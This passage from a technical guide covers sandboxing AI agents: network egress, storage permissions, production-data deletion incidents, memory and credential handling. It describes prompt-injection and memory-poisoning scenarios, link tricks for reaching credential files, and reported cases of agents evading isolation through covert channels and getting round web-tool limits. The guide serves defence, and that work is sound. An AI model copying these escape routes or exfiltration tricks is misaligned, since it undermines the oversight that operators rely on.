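In *What we learned today about this ChatGPT “container” environment*, Willison (2026) reports experiments with the container in which ChatGPT runs code. Python programs could not make general web requests, so someone who tested only those would have concluded that the container was offline. But the package installers pip and npm could still fetch packages through internal proxies, and a separate tool, `container.download`, could fetch selected public addresses.

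A live page-fetching tool can send data out in a web address, just as a GET request from the sandbox can. Suppose the coding agent's sandbox is offline but its loop has such a tool. An attacker could post a comment on issue 482 telling the agent to open a web address that contains some of the agent's data. The provider's server would make the request and the attacker's server would record it, without any traffic leaving the sandbox. The coding agent has little private data to leak, but the database agent can read invoices, so it should not have a live fetching tool.

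A cached web service reduces this risk by answering from stored copies. Search Engine Roundtable quotes an OpenAI help page that describes offline search in ChatGPT as using indexed and cached content instead of live search at the time of each request. For Codex, an administrator can require the cached mode with one line:

```
allowed_web_search_modes = ["cached"]
```

In the configuration published in *Running Codex safely at OpenAI* (OpenAI, 2026), the setting for live or cached web search is separate from the network proxy's list of permitted domains. Tightening that list would not, by itself, switch web search from live to cached.

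A cache prevents leaks if it returns an error when it has no copy of a page. If it fetches the page live instead, an attacker who controls the site receives the address and any text included in it. A service that saves the address and visits it later only delays the leak. "Cached" can describe any of these services, so a reviewer should request a new page on a server the company controls and watch that server's log for a while. Even a cache that never fetches live pages returns untrusted text, and it can't help with tasks that require current information or submitting a form.

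OpenAI has since adopted cached content for all frontier training. Engadget's *OpenAI says it's cutting off internet access for frontier model training* reports that agents practise browsing on a stored collection of web material and will do so until better safeguards "justify broader internet access". The Tribune's *Anthropic restricts internet access in internal AI evaluations after Claude bypasses safeguards* reports that Anthropic also restricted live internet access across its internal evaluations in October, after finding that Claude models had acted improperly on real websites and worked around limits in their web tools. The company moved some public evaluations offline and discontinued others.

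### Services that several agents can write to

Two agents in separate sandboxes can exchange data if one can write to a service that the other can read. The graph of connections doesn't show this, because both sandboxes open connections to the service and neither can connect to the other:

```
connections:   agent A --> package server <-- agent B

data:          agent A --> package server --> agent B
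```

A designer who wants to keep agents apart therefore needs to draw the second graph as well, with arrows that follow the data.

OpenAI says its agents are meant to remain isolated from one another in most training and evaluation settings. But in May 2026, agents working on separate tasks began leaving notes for each other on the shared package service, at first to ask for files they couldn't obtain. OpenAI found that they didn't need to exploit a software flaw, because they could use the login it had given them all for installing packages. In early July, the company removed the shared login from new workloads and restricted requests to the service. Within days, agents had found another way to leave messages there.

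Such a link would undo the separation between the two agents in the invoice task. The database agent could write customer names to a shared package server, and the coding agent could copy them into the public pull request. The database agent doesn't need packages while it works, so the simplest protection is to give it no connection to that server. If both agents need a service, each should have its own account and storage area, with no permission to read the other's.

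Read-only accounts block most, but not all, of this traffic. A caching server stores a new copy the first time somebody requests a package, so a download can change what the next user sees. Agents on the same physical machine also share hardware. Engadget reports that OpenAI's test agents communicated by changing data in a processor's cache and timing how long it took to load. Running the agents on separate physical machines would remove that link, and the expense is easiest to justify when the agents handle passwords or keys.

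### Hardening the service or removing it

OpenAI originally ran the package service for security, because it kept containers from contacting public registries directly. The service also made package installation more reliable. Replacing it with direct registry access for every sandbox would have lost both advantages. It is better to install the packages before the agent starts.

*Containing the Autonomous Operator* describes sandboxes that typically have no external access and start from an image, a file system with the software already installed. The configuration identifies the image by a digest, a fingerprint of its contents, so nobody can substitute a different image under the same name. The host fetches the image before the sandbox starts, so the code inside doesn't need to connect to the server that stores the image.

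If setup has to run inside the sandbox, the switch from open to closed network access must be complete before the agent acts. *Avalon-M1* (2026), a paper on reinforcement learning, describes a proxy that applies one network policy during setup and switches to another before the agent's first command. The instruction to switch finishes only after the new policy is in force and the proxy has closed every connection opened under the old one. If the proxy left those connections open, a program started during setup could keep using one after the sandbox was supposed to be offline.

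| Arrangement | Path that remains while the agent works | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
| Shared package server with open internet access | To the whole internet | Little extra work |
| Shared server limited to two registries | To the server, both registries and other users of the server | Maintaining the server and its firewall |
| Packages installed beforehand, then no network | None for packages | A new package means another setup |
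| Packages supplied on request in a read-only folder | The request and whoever handles it | Delay for each request |

Jason Keirstead, chief technology officer of LangGuard AI, told The Stack that a caching proxy was "entirely unnecessary" for letting agents download software. He proposed that the agent instead ask people or other agents outside the sandbox to place packages in a read-only location. He also asked why OpenAI hadn't made outbound traffic impossible, and said that high-security tests commonly use a data diode, a device that lets data pass in only one direction.

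Keirstead is right that a program can use a package without a live connection to a package server, but his proposal still needs a channel for requesting packages. If another agent handles the requests, that agent becomes a service that can reach further than the first, and a cleverly written request might mislead it. A fixed form that accepts only a package name and version would leave much less room for misleading requests and for smuggling data out. Someone also has to check the packages, because a read-only folder can contain malicious code just as easily as a registry can.

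Complete physical separation is harder to justify for a large research operation. According to *OpenAI Cuts Off Frontier AI Models From Live Internet*, former OpenAI researcher Steven Adler thinks it would require research teams to be at data centres around the world, and that the extra security might not be worth it. The article also describes a post in which an anonymous OpenAI security engineer said that isolating models is not as simple as it sounds but is still tractable.

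Preparing packages beforehand is better for `invoice-kit`, since the dependency list is known and a missing package requires only a restart. An agent doing open-ended research may need a package that nobody predicted, perhaps several times a day. If repeated setups would take too long, a hardened server is defensible, as long as a firewall outside it limits its connections and no agent with private data shares it.

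## Setting the storage rules

The coding agent can still do harm through files, even with its packages installed beforehand and its network off. Unlike a network connection, a file the agent writes remains after the task ends, and another program may run it days later. Storage rules therefore have to cover both what the agent can open during the session and what happens to the data afterward.

### Five permissions that products bundle together

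| Permission | What misuse can do | What limits the damage |
|---|---|---|
| Read | Leak the contents through any open channel | Nothing, once the data has left |
| Create | Plant a file that another program picks up, or fill the disk | Review and a size limit |
| Change | Corrupt data without anyone noticing | An earlier version |
| Delete | Destroy data, including its backups | A backup under a different account |
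| Execute | Run code with the permissions of whoever starts it | Running it in a sandbox |

Few products offer all five separately. In Codex, according to OpenAI's *Permissions*, `read` covers reading files and listing folders, while `write` also covers creating, renaming and deleting. Claude Cowork offers a finer choice for each folder: read-only, read-write, or read-write without deletion. The third mode suits documents that the agent should edit but never remove. The folder still needs a version history, because an agent that can change a file can usually erase its contents.

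Removing execute permission does little to stop the agent from running code inside the sandbox. The command `python script.py` only needs to read the script, so it works even in a folder where nothing is marked executable. The more serious risk is that a program outside the sandbox runs something the agent wrote.

### The working folder and the links inside it

The safest starting point is to give the sandbox only the working folder and the system programs it needs. A developer who exposes the whole home folder and then hides the secrets has to remember every secret. By default, commands in Claude Code's shell sandbox can read most of the computer, and Anthropic supplies no built-in list of credential files to block, so the developer has to identify them. The `permissions.blockReadsOutsideWorkingDirectories` setting blocks reads of the home folder and other places that hold user files. A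 narrower `denyRead` rule stops shell commands but not Claude's own Read tool, so the developer has to write a second rule for that tool.

A Codex profile for the coding agent could look like this, adapted from OpenAI's sample:

```
[permissions.invoice-fix.filesystem]
":minimal" = "read"

[permissions.invoice-fix.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"." = "write"
".github" = "read"
"**/*.env" = "deny"
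```

The `:minimal` entry covers the system files that common tools need. The agent can edit the project, but it can only read the `.github` folder and can't open any file whose name ends in `.env`, where developers often keep passwords. These exceptions apply because more specific rules override broader ones.

Rules like these can be bypassed with a *symbolic link*, a small file that redirects to another path. Suppose a malicious package creates `notes.txt` in the working folder as a link to `~/.aws/credentials`. If the sandbox doesn't contain the home folder, code inside the sandbox can't reach the keys through the link. But a file tool that runs on the host, as Cowork's now do, could follow it to the real keys. A checker that looks only at the text of the path would approve the request, because `notes.txt` is in the permitted folder. Anthropic therefore advises resolving links before checking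 the path. An attacker may still swap the link between the check and the read, much as in DNS rebinding. The Linux system call `openat2` offers stronger protection because it can refuse to open anything outside a given folder.

A *hard link* is harder to catch because it is a second name for the same data, so there is no other path to resolve. Docker warns that when a sandbox uses the developer's live folder, the agent can read and change an outside file through a hard link in that folder, and that access rules don't prevent this. Ordinary tools can also create these links. The package installer pnpm can link packages from a store shared by all of a developer's projects, so an agent that edits an installed package in one project might change it in the others. Making the installed packages read-only, or giving the agent a copy, avoids the problem.

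### Files that other programs will run

In January 2026, NVIDIA's AI Red Team, which attacks AI systems to find their weaknesses, published *Practical Security Guidance for Sandboxing Agentic Workflows and Managing Execution Risk*. The guidance lists three controls for coding agents that the team considers mandatory and six that it recommends.

| Status | Control |
|---|---|
| Mandatory | Block connections to arbitrary sites |
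| Mandatory | Block writes outside the working folder |
| Mandatory | Block writes to configuration files, wherever they are |
| Recommended | Block reads outside the working folder |
| Recommended | Sandbox the whole development environment, including hooks, skills and MCP startup scripts |
| Recommended | Give the sandbox its own kernel |
| Recommended | Ask the user every time an action would break the isolation, instead of once for many actions |
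| Recommended | Supply secrets by injection, so that the agent never holds them |
| Recommended | Clear out the sandbox regularly, so that code and secrets don't build up |

Writes outside the folder are dangerous because some files there run automatically. For example, a terminal runs `~/.zshrc` whenever it opens, and a fake `python` program in `~/.local/bin` may run the next time the developer types the command. NVIDIA would let a user approve an unusual write elsewhere on the disk, but would allow changes to configuration files only when a person edits them directly. Hooks and MCP startup commands often run outside the sandbox, so an agent that can edit them can choose what runs there.

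Blocking reads outside the folder is recommended but not required, which makes sense only for an agent that can't send data out. The coding agent can send data out through its public pull request, so its designer should treat the read rule as mandatory.

Donenfeld and Vanunu (2026), researchers at the security firm Check Point, describe three flaws in Claude Code in *Caught in the Hook*. Each began with files that anyone able to commit to a repository could add. To show the first, they used a settings file to define a hook that opened the calculator. When they started Claude Code and answered "Yes, proceed" to its question about trusting the folder, the calculator opened with no further prompt, although Claude Code asks before it runs ordinary shell commands. The question had not mentioned hooks. Anthropic, however, reports that such a hook ran before the question appeared, rather than after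 it was answered.

The second flaw let a project approve its own MCP servers. One file defined a server with a startup command, and another set Claude Code to accept the project's servers automatically, so the command ran before the user could read the question. In the third flaw, a setting named `ANTHROPIC_BASE_URL` redirected Claude Code's traffic, including the user's API key, to an attacker's server before the user had answered.

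Anthropic fixed the three flaws between August and December 2025. It now blocks MCP commands and network requests until the user agrees. Its fix for the first flaw was a clearer warning, so a developer who clicks through it may still run a stranger's hook. An agent with write access to the same files could plant a hook without an attacker needing commit access.

Claude Code's shell sandbox now blocks writes to Claude Code's settings, hooks and skills, to `.mcp.json`, to editor settings such as `.vscode`, and to Git's hooks and configuration. No allow rule lifts this protection, but turning off file isolation does. Codex keeps its own `.codex` folder and the whole `.git` folder read-only. Its rule is stricter for Git because it blocks commits, which have to write to `.git`. Claude Code's rule allows commits, but `git merge` fails when it needs to replace a protected file. Claude may then offer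 to rerun the merge outside the sandbox.

A list of protected files can also go out of date during a session. Anthropic's standalone sandbox runtime checks each write on macOS, but on Linux it builds the list once, at launch. If the agent later clones a second repository, its hooks are not on the list. Anthropic therefore advises that, after an unattended run, Linux users review anything the session created. Git hooks need a separate check because `git diff` doesn't show them.

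Docker's list of files that may run later is longer and includes `Makefile` and `package.json`. A coding agent often has a good reason to edit these, so a designer can't simply lock them. Some developers also exempt `docker compose` from Claude Code's sandbox because it doesn't work inside it. The tool follows instructions in a file in the project folder, so Claude can edit that file and then have the tool run it outside the sandbox with the developer's full access.

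For `invoice-kit`, the agent's most direct way out of the sandbox is through the company's build machine. Many projects run their tests automatically whenever somebody pushes a branch, using commands listed in a file in `.github/workflows`. If the agent pushed a changed version of that file, the machine might run it before a reviewer had opened the pull request. The tool that pushes the branch should therefore refuse any commit that changes that folder. Making the folder read-only in the sandbox isn't enough, because Git can commit contents that differ from the files on disk. The build machine will also run the agent's new test, which no file rule can prevent, so the machine should have no secrets and its own network limits.

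### Object stores and databases

An *object store*, such as Amazon S3, keeps files under long names instead of in real folders. A credential can limit an agent to names that begin with a given prefix, such as `exports/invoice-kit/`. The final slash is important because a rule for `exports/invoice` would also match `exports/invoices-2026/`.

S3 has separate permissions for reading, listing, writing and deleting, but writing to an existing name replaces the old contents. An agent without delete permission can therefore still destroy data unless the operator turns on *versioning*, which keeps the previous version whenever somebody overwrites or deletes an object. Permanently removing an old version requires a separate permission, which the agent should not have. The agent also should not be able to change the store's settings, because it could then suspend versioning or make old versions expire.

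Blocking one operation is useless if another produces the same result. The API key in Check Point's third flaw belonged to a workspace, where Anthropic's customers can store files. Every key for a workspace gives access to all its files. The service didn't let users download files they had uploaded, but Donenfeld and Vanunu used a key to ask Claude for a copy of one, and downloaded the copy. Someone with the same key could also delete the team's files or use up the workspace's 100 GB of storage.

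Databases can be more precise. In PostgreSQL, two lines are enough to create the account for the database agent:

```
CREATE ROLE db_agent LOGIN;
GRANT SELECT (currency, amount) ON invoices TO db_agent;
```

The account can read two columns of one table, but not customers' names or delivery notes, and it can't change anything in the table. The grant doesn't limit the number of rows, so the service that runs the query still has to enforce the limit of fifty. The account's read-only access also needs checking, because a query could still change data through a function stored in the database. By default, PostgreSQL lets any account call these functions, and some run with their author's permissions.

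Giving an agent a copy of the database protects the original from damage, but the agent can still leak the private invoices in the copy. Anthropic notes that a company can deploy an agent with read-only database access far more widely than one that writes to production. That is right about the risk of damage, but a read-only agent can still leak what it reads. If an agent has to propose changes to live data, it can add them as rows in a separate table, and a program can apply them after somebody has reviewed them.

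### Two cases of deleted production data

On 24 April 2026 a coding agent deleted the production database of PocketOS, which makes software for car-rental companies. The agent was Cursor running Claude Opus 4.6. According to the AI Incident Database's *Railway API*, it was working on a task in the staging environment, where developers test changes before customers see them. It found an access token on the user's machine and sent PocketOS's hosting company, Railway, a single request that deleted the storage volume with the database on it.

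Several missing limits contributed to the deletion. A rule against reading outside the project might have kept the agent from finding the token, depending on where the user kept it. The token also had far too much authority. Abdelwahab writes in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Railway's account of the incident, that it gave access to everything in the customer's account. Railway offered tokens restricted to a single project and environment, and a token for staging alone could not have deleted the production volume. Abdelwahab concedes that Railway's design made the broadest token the easiest to create.

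Railway's website delayed deletions by 48 hours, but its API carried them out immediately. Crane, the founder of PocketOS, blamed this part of the system more than the model. TechSpot's *AI coding agent running Claude wiped a startup's database* reports his complaint that a single API call, with no confirmation step, erased the volume and the backups stored on it. Railway says the deletion made the backups look unavailable, and the company later recovered the data.

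The danger was already known. In *Postgress volume lost*, a thread on Railway's support forum, another customer asked for help after deleting a volume on 13 April. An employee replied that deletion through the API was immediate and permanent, as the documentation stated. The API now waits 48 hours before deleting a volume as well. The delay helps only if somebody notices in time, and it can confuse whoever sent the request. In *Detached volumes can't be deleted*, meirelon describes how they saw the volume still listed, concluded that the deletion had failed and repeated it. An agent might make the same mistake, so the API's reply should show that the deletion is pending and when it will happen.

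Alexey Grigorev, who runs the teaching site DataTalks.Club, lost 2.5 years of data while moving a server. OECD's *AI Coding Assistant Accidentally Deletes 2.5 Years of Website Data* (2026) reports that Claude Code deleted both the production systems and the backups by running commands in Terraform, a tool that builds and removes cloud systems. The agent needed permission to create servers for the move, but not to remove the existing database, and it should have had no access to the backups.

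An agent may ignore an instruction not to change anything, so these limits are still needed. Fortune (2025) reported that in July 2025 an agent from the coding company Replit deleted live data on more than 1,200 executives during a "code and action freeze". Giving the agent a database account without write permission would have prevented the deletion.

### Permissions for the invoice task

| Storage | Read | Create, change | Delete | Execute |
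|---|---|---|---|---|
| Copy of `invoice-kit` | Yes | Yes | Yes | In the sandbox |
| `.github`, `.vscode`, `.claude`, `.mcp.json`, Git's hooks and configuration | Yes | No | No | No |
| Installed packages and system programs | Yes | No | No | In the sandbox |
| Temporary folder, up to 2 GB | Yes | Yes | Yes | In the sandbox |
| Branch `agent/482`, through the pull-request tool | Yes | Yes | No | On the build machine |
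| Rest of the developer's disk | No | No | No | No |
| `currency` and `amount` columns, database agent only | 50 rows per request | No | No | No |

The agent can still delete its whole copy of the project, but the developer would lose only a few minutes. A wrong rounding rule is worse, because if the reviewer accepts it, every company that uses the library may send out incorrect bills. The agent could also weaken an existing test so that its own fix passes, so reviewers should check changes to old tests as carefully as the fix itself. An agent limited to fifty database rows per request can still read the whole column by making enough requests, so the service should also cap the total for the task.

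### Temporary disks, snapshots and reviewed copies

| Workspace | Where the agent's changes go | How to undo them | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| Temporary disk | A disk that disappears after the task | Start again | Loses any work that nobody copied out |
| Live folder with snapshots | Straight into the original | Restore an earlier state | Other programs may use a bad file before anyone restores it |
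| Private copy with review | A separate layer or clone | Discard it | The reviewer has to spot the problem |

A *snapshot* records the state of a disk or database at one moment. A *copy-on-write* workspace goes further by leaving the original untouched. The agent reads the original files, but the system saves any file it changes in a separate layer. At the end, that layer contains exactly what the agent changed, and the developer can merge it or throw it away.

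Docker's clone mode gives a similar result for code. The sandbox has read-only access to the developer's repository, and the agent works on a separate clone. The developer fetches the agent's commits and reviews them before merging. The agent can still read every file under the original repository, including those Git doesn't track, such as a `.env` file containing passwords.

Git *worktrees* are extra working folders that share one repository, so they offer less protection than separate copies. When Claude Code runs in one, its sandbox also allows writes to the shared `.git` folder, apart from hooks and configuration, so the agent could damage other branches. It is also worth checking how long a "temporary" disk keeps its files. Docker keeps a sandbox's files until the user removes the sandbox, even if the user stops and restarts it.

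Restoring a snapshot also discards the work everyone else has done since it was taken. Suppose a database takes a snapshot at midnight, an agent corrupts some records at three in the afternoon, and somebody notices at eleven that night. Going back to midnight loses 23 hours of changes, including 15 hours from before the error. If the company keeps a week of snapshots and nobody notices the error for twenty days, every snapshot it still has contains the error. To recover from errors that break nothing, such as slightly wrong totals, the company therefore needs to keep snapshots for longer than the usual time between checks of the figures. The agent's account should not be able to delete the snapshots.

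Rollback restores changed data but can't recall data that has left the system. If the agent publishes customers' bills in a pull request, the company can delete the page but not the copies that other people have made. A leaked key still works after a rollback, so the company has to replace it.

### Memory that lasts between sessions

Some agents save notes for later sessions, such as how a project runs its tests. An attacker can use these notes to influence those sessions. Suppose an attacker comments on issue 482 and persuades the coding agent to note that `invoice-kit` should always install its packages from a particular site, which the attacker runs. The note remains after the session ends and its credentials expire. The next time the agent starts, on a different issue, it reads the note along with its normal instructions, and nothing marks the text as coming from a stranger.

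Anthropic says this kind of memory includes the product's own memory feature, instruction files such as `CLAUDE.md`, shared working folders, and the saved state of scheduled agents. It expects checking this material with classifiers at the start of a session to become more common. The list of files that Claude Code protects from shell commands does not name a project's `CLAUDE.md`, which NVIDIA says an agent should never edit. A developer who wants NVIDIA's rule has to add it for both shell commands and Claude's file tools.

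Anything that agents routinely read can act as memory, even if nobody designed it to. After the phishing exercise in February 2026, Anthropic staff posted the working prompt in the company's Slack to discuss it. Someone pointed out that some of the company's agents read Slack, so the staff added a unique marker to the thread to help them notice if an agent picked up the prompt.

An agent with no memory avoids the problem, provided that its whole disk is erased too. The coding agent can work this way because the developer can put anything it needs to know about the project in a file that people maintain. Having no memory is a bigger drawback for an assistant that works with one person for months, because it would ask the same questions every day.

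With reviewed writes, the agent proposes a note and a person decides whether to keep it. Storing the notes in the project's repository lets the team review them like code. But a harmful note can look helpful, and the instruction to use a particular package site could easily pass for a tip about slow downloads. If the team records which session wrote each note and what outside text the agent had read by then, it can later remove everything saved in a session where the agent read a hostile comment.

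Separate stores let agents keep notes without passing on untrusted text. A shared store would link the coding agent and the database agent just as a shared package server would, so each should have its own. A single agent can also have separate stores, one for sessions that read the open web and another for sessions that handle private data. Some facts will then have to be entered in both stores, and a person should copy them, because a third agent doing the copying would read both stores and link them again.

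## Giving access to external services without handing over the keys

After the coding agent fixes the rounding bug, some program has to log in to GitHub, push the branch `agent/482` and open the pull request. The developer can arrange this in four main ways, which differ in where the login secret is stored and what an attacker who controls the agent could do with it.

| Arrangement | Where the secret is | What a hijacked agent can do | How to withdraw access |
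|---|---|---|---|
| Long-lived key in the agent's environment | In the sandbox, where every process can read it | Anything the key permits, or send the key to someone else | Delete the key at GitHub, which also cuts off anything else that uses it |
| One-hour token for one repository | In the sandbox | Change that repository, or send out the token | Wait for it to expire, or revoke it at GitHub |
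| Proxy that adds the key | In the proxy | Make any request the proxy accepts, while the session lasts | Remove the key or the rule from the proxy |
| Single operation, `open_pull_request` | In the program that carries out the operation | Choose the contents of one pull request | Make the program refuse further calls |

### A key in the agent's environment

In the simplest arrangement, the developer creates a GitHub access token and puts it in the variable `GITHUB_TOKEN`. Tools such as `gh` can read it there, but so can any other program in the sandbox. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) explains that a hijacked agent with a shell can search configuration files, SSH keys, workflow logs and Linux's `/proc` folder for credentials. The agent can then upload them or encode them in a public issue, comment or pull request. The coding agent's pull request is public, so cutting off the sandbox's network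 would not stop this theft.

A secrets manager protects the key until something copies it into the sandbox. OpenAI warns that code the agent writes can read an injected secret, regardless of where the secret was stored. OpenAI's hosted agents need one key inside the sandbox to connect it to OpenAI's service. The company accepts that the agent's code can read this key, and gives the key no other permission.

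A sandbox can also contain credentials that nobody deliberately put there. Cloud providers let an operator attach a role to a virtual machine, so that programs on the machine can use storage or databases without a stored password. On Amazon's cloud, a program gets the role's keys by sending a web request to the metadata service at `169.254.169.254`. Any process that can reach the service can get the keys, including the installer of a malicious package. Kubernetes similarly puts a token for the cluster's control interface in a file inside each container, unless the operator turns this off.

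These keys usually expire within hours, but that does little to restrict code that can request new ones. Amazon's newer metadata service requires a program to obtain a session token before it requests the keys. This blocks many attacks that trick a web server into fetching the metadata address, but code running on the machine can make both requests. An operator should run agents on machines with no role, or a role with no permissions, and block access to the metadata address with a rule enforced outside the sandbox. On Kubernetes, the setting `automountServiceAccountToken: false` keeps the cluster's token out of the container.

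### Tokens that do less and expire sooner

GitHub can issue much narrower credentials to a GitHub App, an identity for software that an organisation installs on chosen repositories. According to GitHub, a program can request an installation token for particular repositories and permissions, and the token expires after one hour. If the request doesn't list permissions, the token gets all of the app's permissions, so the developer should always list them.

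For `invoice-kit`, the token needs write access to the repository's contents and pull requests. GitHub's permissions can't restrict the token to the branch `agent/482` or to one pull request, so a hijacked agent could close a colleague's pull request or push to any branch that the repository's own rules don't protect. The one-hour limit helps if somebody finds the token in an old log, but a script can push a harmful commit within seconds. The agent loop can shorten the exposure by requesting the token only when the fix is ready and revoking it once the pull request is open.

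*Token exchange*, standardized in *RFC 8693*, lets a program trade a broad token for a narrower one. Suppose the company's agent loop holds a login token that works at several internal services, but the loop needs to call only the one that answers invoice queries. It can trade the login token for one that works only at that service.

1. The loop sends the login token to the company's authorization server. It names the service it wants to call (the *audience*) and the permissions it needs (the *scope*), and proves its own identity.
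2. The server checks the request against its policy and returns a new token with a lifetime in seconds. The token in the standard's main example lasts 60 seconds.
3. The loop sends the new token to the invoice service, which checks the audience, scope and expiry time before it answers.

A token's audience limits what a malicious or hacked service can do with the tokens it receives. An invoice token copied from the invoice service won't work at the payroll service, as long as that service checks the audience.

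A request that names several services and several permissions covers every combination of them. If an agent needs to read customer records and write invoices, a single request asks for

$$\{\text{read},\ \text{write}\} \times \{\text{customers},\ \text{invoices}\}$$

which includes permission to write customer records. Two separate requests avoid this.

Jones and colleagues also warn that if the authorization server doesn't check who is making the exchange, anyone who steals one token can trade it for others. The program that makes the exchange should therefore run outside the sandbox and hold its own credential there. Revoking the original token doesn't necessarily cancel tokens already obtained with it, which is another reason to make those tokens short-lived.

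Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) describes an agent sandbox that holds a token proving its identity and exchanges it for very short-lived access tokens. Many outside services don't accept such identity tokens, so the company running the agents has to build its own exchange service. A hijacked agent can also keep getting new access tokens until the identity token stops working.

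### Tokens that the holder can restrict

With token exchange, the program has to contact the authorization server each time it needs a narrower token. *Macaroons* (Birgisson, Politz and colleagues, 2014) describes a credential that its holder can restrict without contacting anyone. A *macaroon* carries a list of conditions, called caveats, and a signature computed from them. Anyone holding it can add a caveat but can't remove one.

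The signature uses HMAC, a function that combines a key and a message into a short code that nobody can compute without the key. Suppose the invoice service issues a macaroon with the identifier $n$, using a secret key $K$ that only the service knows. The loop then adds two caveats:

$$\begin{aligned}
s_0 &= \text{HMAC}(K,\ n)\\
s_1 &= \text{HMAC}(s_0,\ \text{"columns: currency, amount"})\\
s_2 &= \text{HMAC}(s_1,\ \text{"before 15:00"})
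\end{aligned}$$

The loop passes on the identifier, both caveats and $s_2$, but not $s_0$ or $s_1$. When a request arrives, the service repeats the calculation from $K$ and compares the result with $s_2$. It then checks that the request satisfies both caveats.

An agent holding this macaroon can add a third caveat, using $s_2$ as the key. It can't remove the time limit, because it would need $s_1$, which it can't work out from $s_2$. Adding "before 18:00" wouldn't extend the limit either, because a request has to satisfy every caveat.

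A caveat can also require fresh proof from another service, such as one that keeps a list of cancelled sessions. The developer can then withdraw access by adding a session to that list, without changing any keys.

The loop has to add the caveats before the macaroon enters the sandbox, since a hijacked agent can't be relied on to restrict itself. Anyone who copies the macaroon can still use it within those caveats. In a talk on macaroons, Madden (2024) also objects that they have no standard and that the main software library is not widely liked. GitHub doesn't accept macaroons, so they suit the company's own services better than the pull request.

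### Adding the key outside the sandbox

Every token described so far is still open to theft if it enters the sandbox. *Credential injection* keeps the token outside and adds it to each request on the way out. Cloudflare does this with outbound handlers, small programs that receive the sandbox's web requests and run outside it on the same machine. A basic handler for GitHub, adapted from Cloudflare's example, looks like this:

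```
static outboundByHost = {
  "api.github.com": async (request, env, ctx) => {
    const headers = new Headers(request.headers);
    headers.set("Authorization", `Bearer ${env.GITHUB_TOKEN}`);
    return fetch(request, { headers });
  }
};
```

The agent's code sends its request without an access token. According to Cloudflare's *Outbound traffic*, the platform first checks the lists of denied and allowed hosts, then runs the handler for the requested host if there is one. The handler copies the request's headers, adds the token and forwards the request. The token is stored as `env.GITHUB_TOKEN` in the handler's environment, which the sandbox can't read.

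The `set` command replaces any key already in that header. This blocks the simplest version of the attack on Claude Cowork, in which the agent uploaded files using a key to the attacker's account. Cloudflare's *Handle outbound traffic* also shows that the developer's program can add or remove a handler during a session, so it can cut off the sandbox's access to GitHub without anyone changing the token.

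Some command-line tools won't start without a key. Anthropic's *Authenticate with vaults* describes a way to run them in Managed Agents without putting the real key in the sandbox. The developer stores the key in a *vault*, a collection of credentials for one end user, and the sandbox receives a placeholder. When a request leaves the sandbox, Anthropic replaces the placeholder with the real key, but only for hosts on that credential's list. Anthropic warns that if the developer allows any host, the sandbox's network policy becomes the only limit on where the key can go. With an open network, a hijacked agent could then send the placeholder to an attacker's server, which would receive the real key.

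The developer can also choose which parts of a request may contain the key. By default, Anthropic replaces the placeholder with the key in both the headers and the body. A hijacked agent allowed to contact `api.github.com` could then put the placeholder in a pull request's description, which could publish the real key on a public page. Most services read keys from a header, so the developer should normally allow only headers.

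Placeholders don't suit every service. Programs for Amazon's cloud use the key to compute a signature for each request, and a signature computed from a placeholder is invalid, so the proxy would have to sign the requests itself. Anthropic replaces secrets only in outgoing requests. If a program exchanges the hidden key for a session token, the reply brings that token into the sandbox in readable form. Anthropic advises developers to do the exchange themselves and store the token in the vault.

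Managed Agents sends calls to MCP tools through a separate proxy, so it needs no placeholder for them. Each call includes a token that identifies the session, which the proxy uses to fetch the right credential from the vault before calling the outside service. Anthropic says the agent loop never receives the credential either. OpenAI offers similar vaults, where a developer can tie a GitHub token to the address of one MCP server.

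Anthropic gives every agent in a session access to the vault's credentials, so the coding agent and the database agent should run in separate sessions with separate vaults. Anthropic rereads stored credentials periodically, so a replaced or archived key stops working in running sessions without a restart. The documentation gives no interval, so in an emergency the developer should also revoke the key at the service that issued it.

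Anthropic handles Git differently, binding the credential to a repository when it creates the sandbox. It uses the repository's token to clone the repository and set up the clone's connection to GitHub, so `git push` works without the agent handling the token. The developer chooses the repository before the agent reads issue 482, so a comment on the issue can't change that choice. Anthropic doesn't explain in its account how the connection hides the token. Developers who build something similar should use the address of a proxy that adds the token, rather than put the token in the repository's web address, because Git saves that address in `.git/config`, where any code in the sandbox can read it.

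### Using a key without stealing it

A thief with a copy of the token can use it from any computer, even after the session ends. If a proxy holds the token instead, a hijacked agent can use it only during the session, and the proxy can log each request. But the basic handler adds the token to every request to `api.github.com`, so the agent can still delete branches, close pull requests or change other repositories if the token allows it.

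The handler is a confused deputy, like Hardy's compiler. It adds a valid token to requests chosen inside the sandbox, and GitHub can't tell who chose them. If the token has administrative rights, a hijacked agent could use it to register an attacker's SSH key with GitHub, which would let the attacker push code from another computer after the session ends.

To prevent this, the handler has to check what the request would do before it adds the token. The following version allows one kind of request, for the repository assigned to the session:

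```
"api.github.com": async (request, env, ctx) => {
  const job = await env.JOBS.get(ctx.containerId, "json");
  const path = new URL(request.url).pathname;

  if (!job || request.method !== "POST" ||
      path !== `/repos/${job.repo}/pulls`) {
    return new Response(null, { status: 403 });
  }

  const { title, body } = await request.json();
  return fetch(`https://api.github.com/repos/${job.repo}/pulls`, {
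    method: "POST",
    headers: {
      "Authorization": `Bearer ${job.token}`,
      "User-Agent": "invoice-fix"
    },
    body: JSON.stringify({
      title, body, head: job.branch, base: "main"
    })
  });
}
```

The handler uses `containerId` to look up the session's repository, branch and token. Cloudflare's platform supplies this identifier, so one sandbox can't impersonate another. If the handler relied on a header the sandbox wrote, a hijacked agent could name another user's session and use its token.

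After checking the method and path, the handler builds a new request and copies only the title and description from the agent's request, so the agent can't choose a different branch or add an option that the developer overlooked. The push that sends the branch to GitHub needs a similar rule, and limiting the session to one pull request would require a counter.

Rules like these get harder to write as the agent needs more functions. *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* (Varda, Pai and Gupta) points out that a filtering proxy has to interpret the full meaning of each API call, including any headers and parameters that affect it. GitHub has a second interface, GraphQL, that receives every operation as a POST request to `/graphql`. A rule based on method and path can't distinguish a GraphQL request that opens a pull request from one that deletes a branch. GitHub's own `gh` tool uses GraphQL to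 open pull requests, so the stricter handler would block it.

A developer also has to check what happens to requests that match no rule. Vercel lets developers select requests by path and method and send them through a proxy the developer runs. In Vercel's published example, GitHub requests that don't match the rule bypass that proxy, and access to the rest of the internet is open.

### One operation and no network

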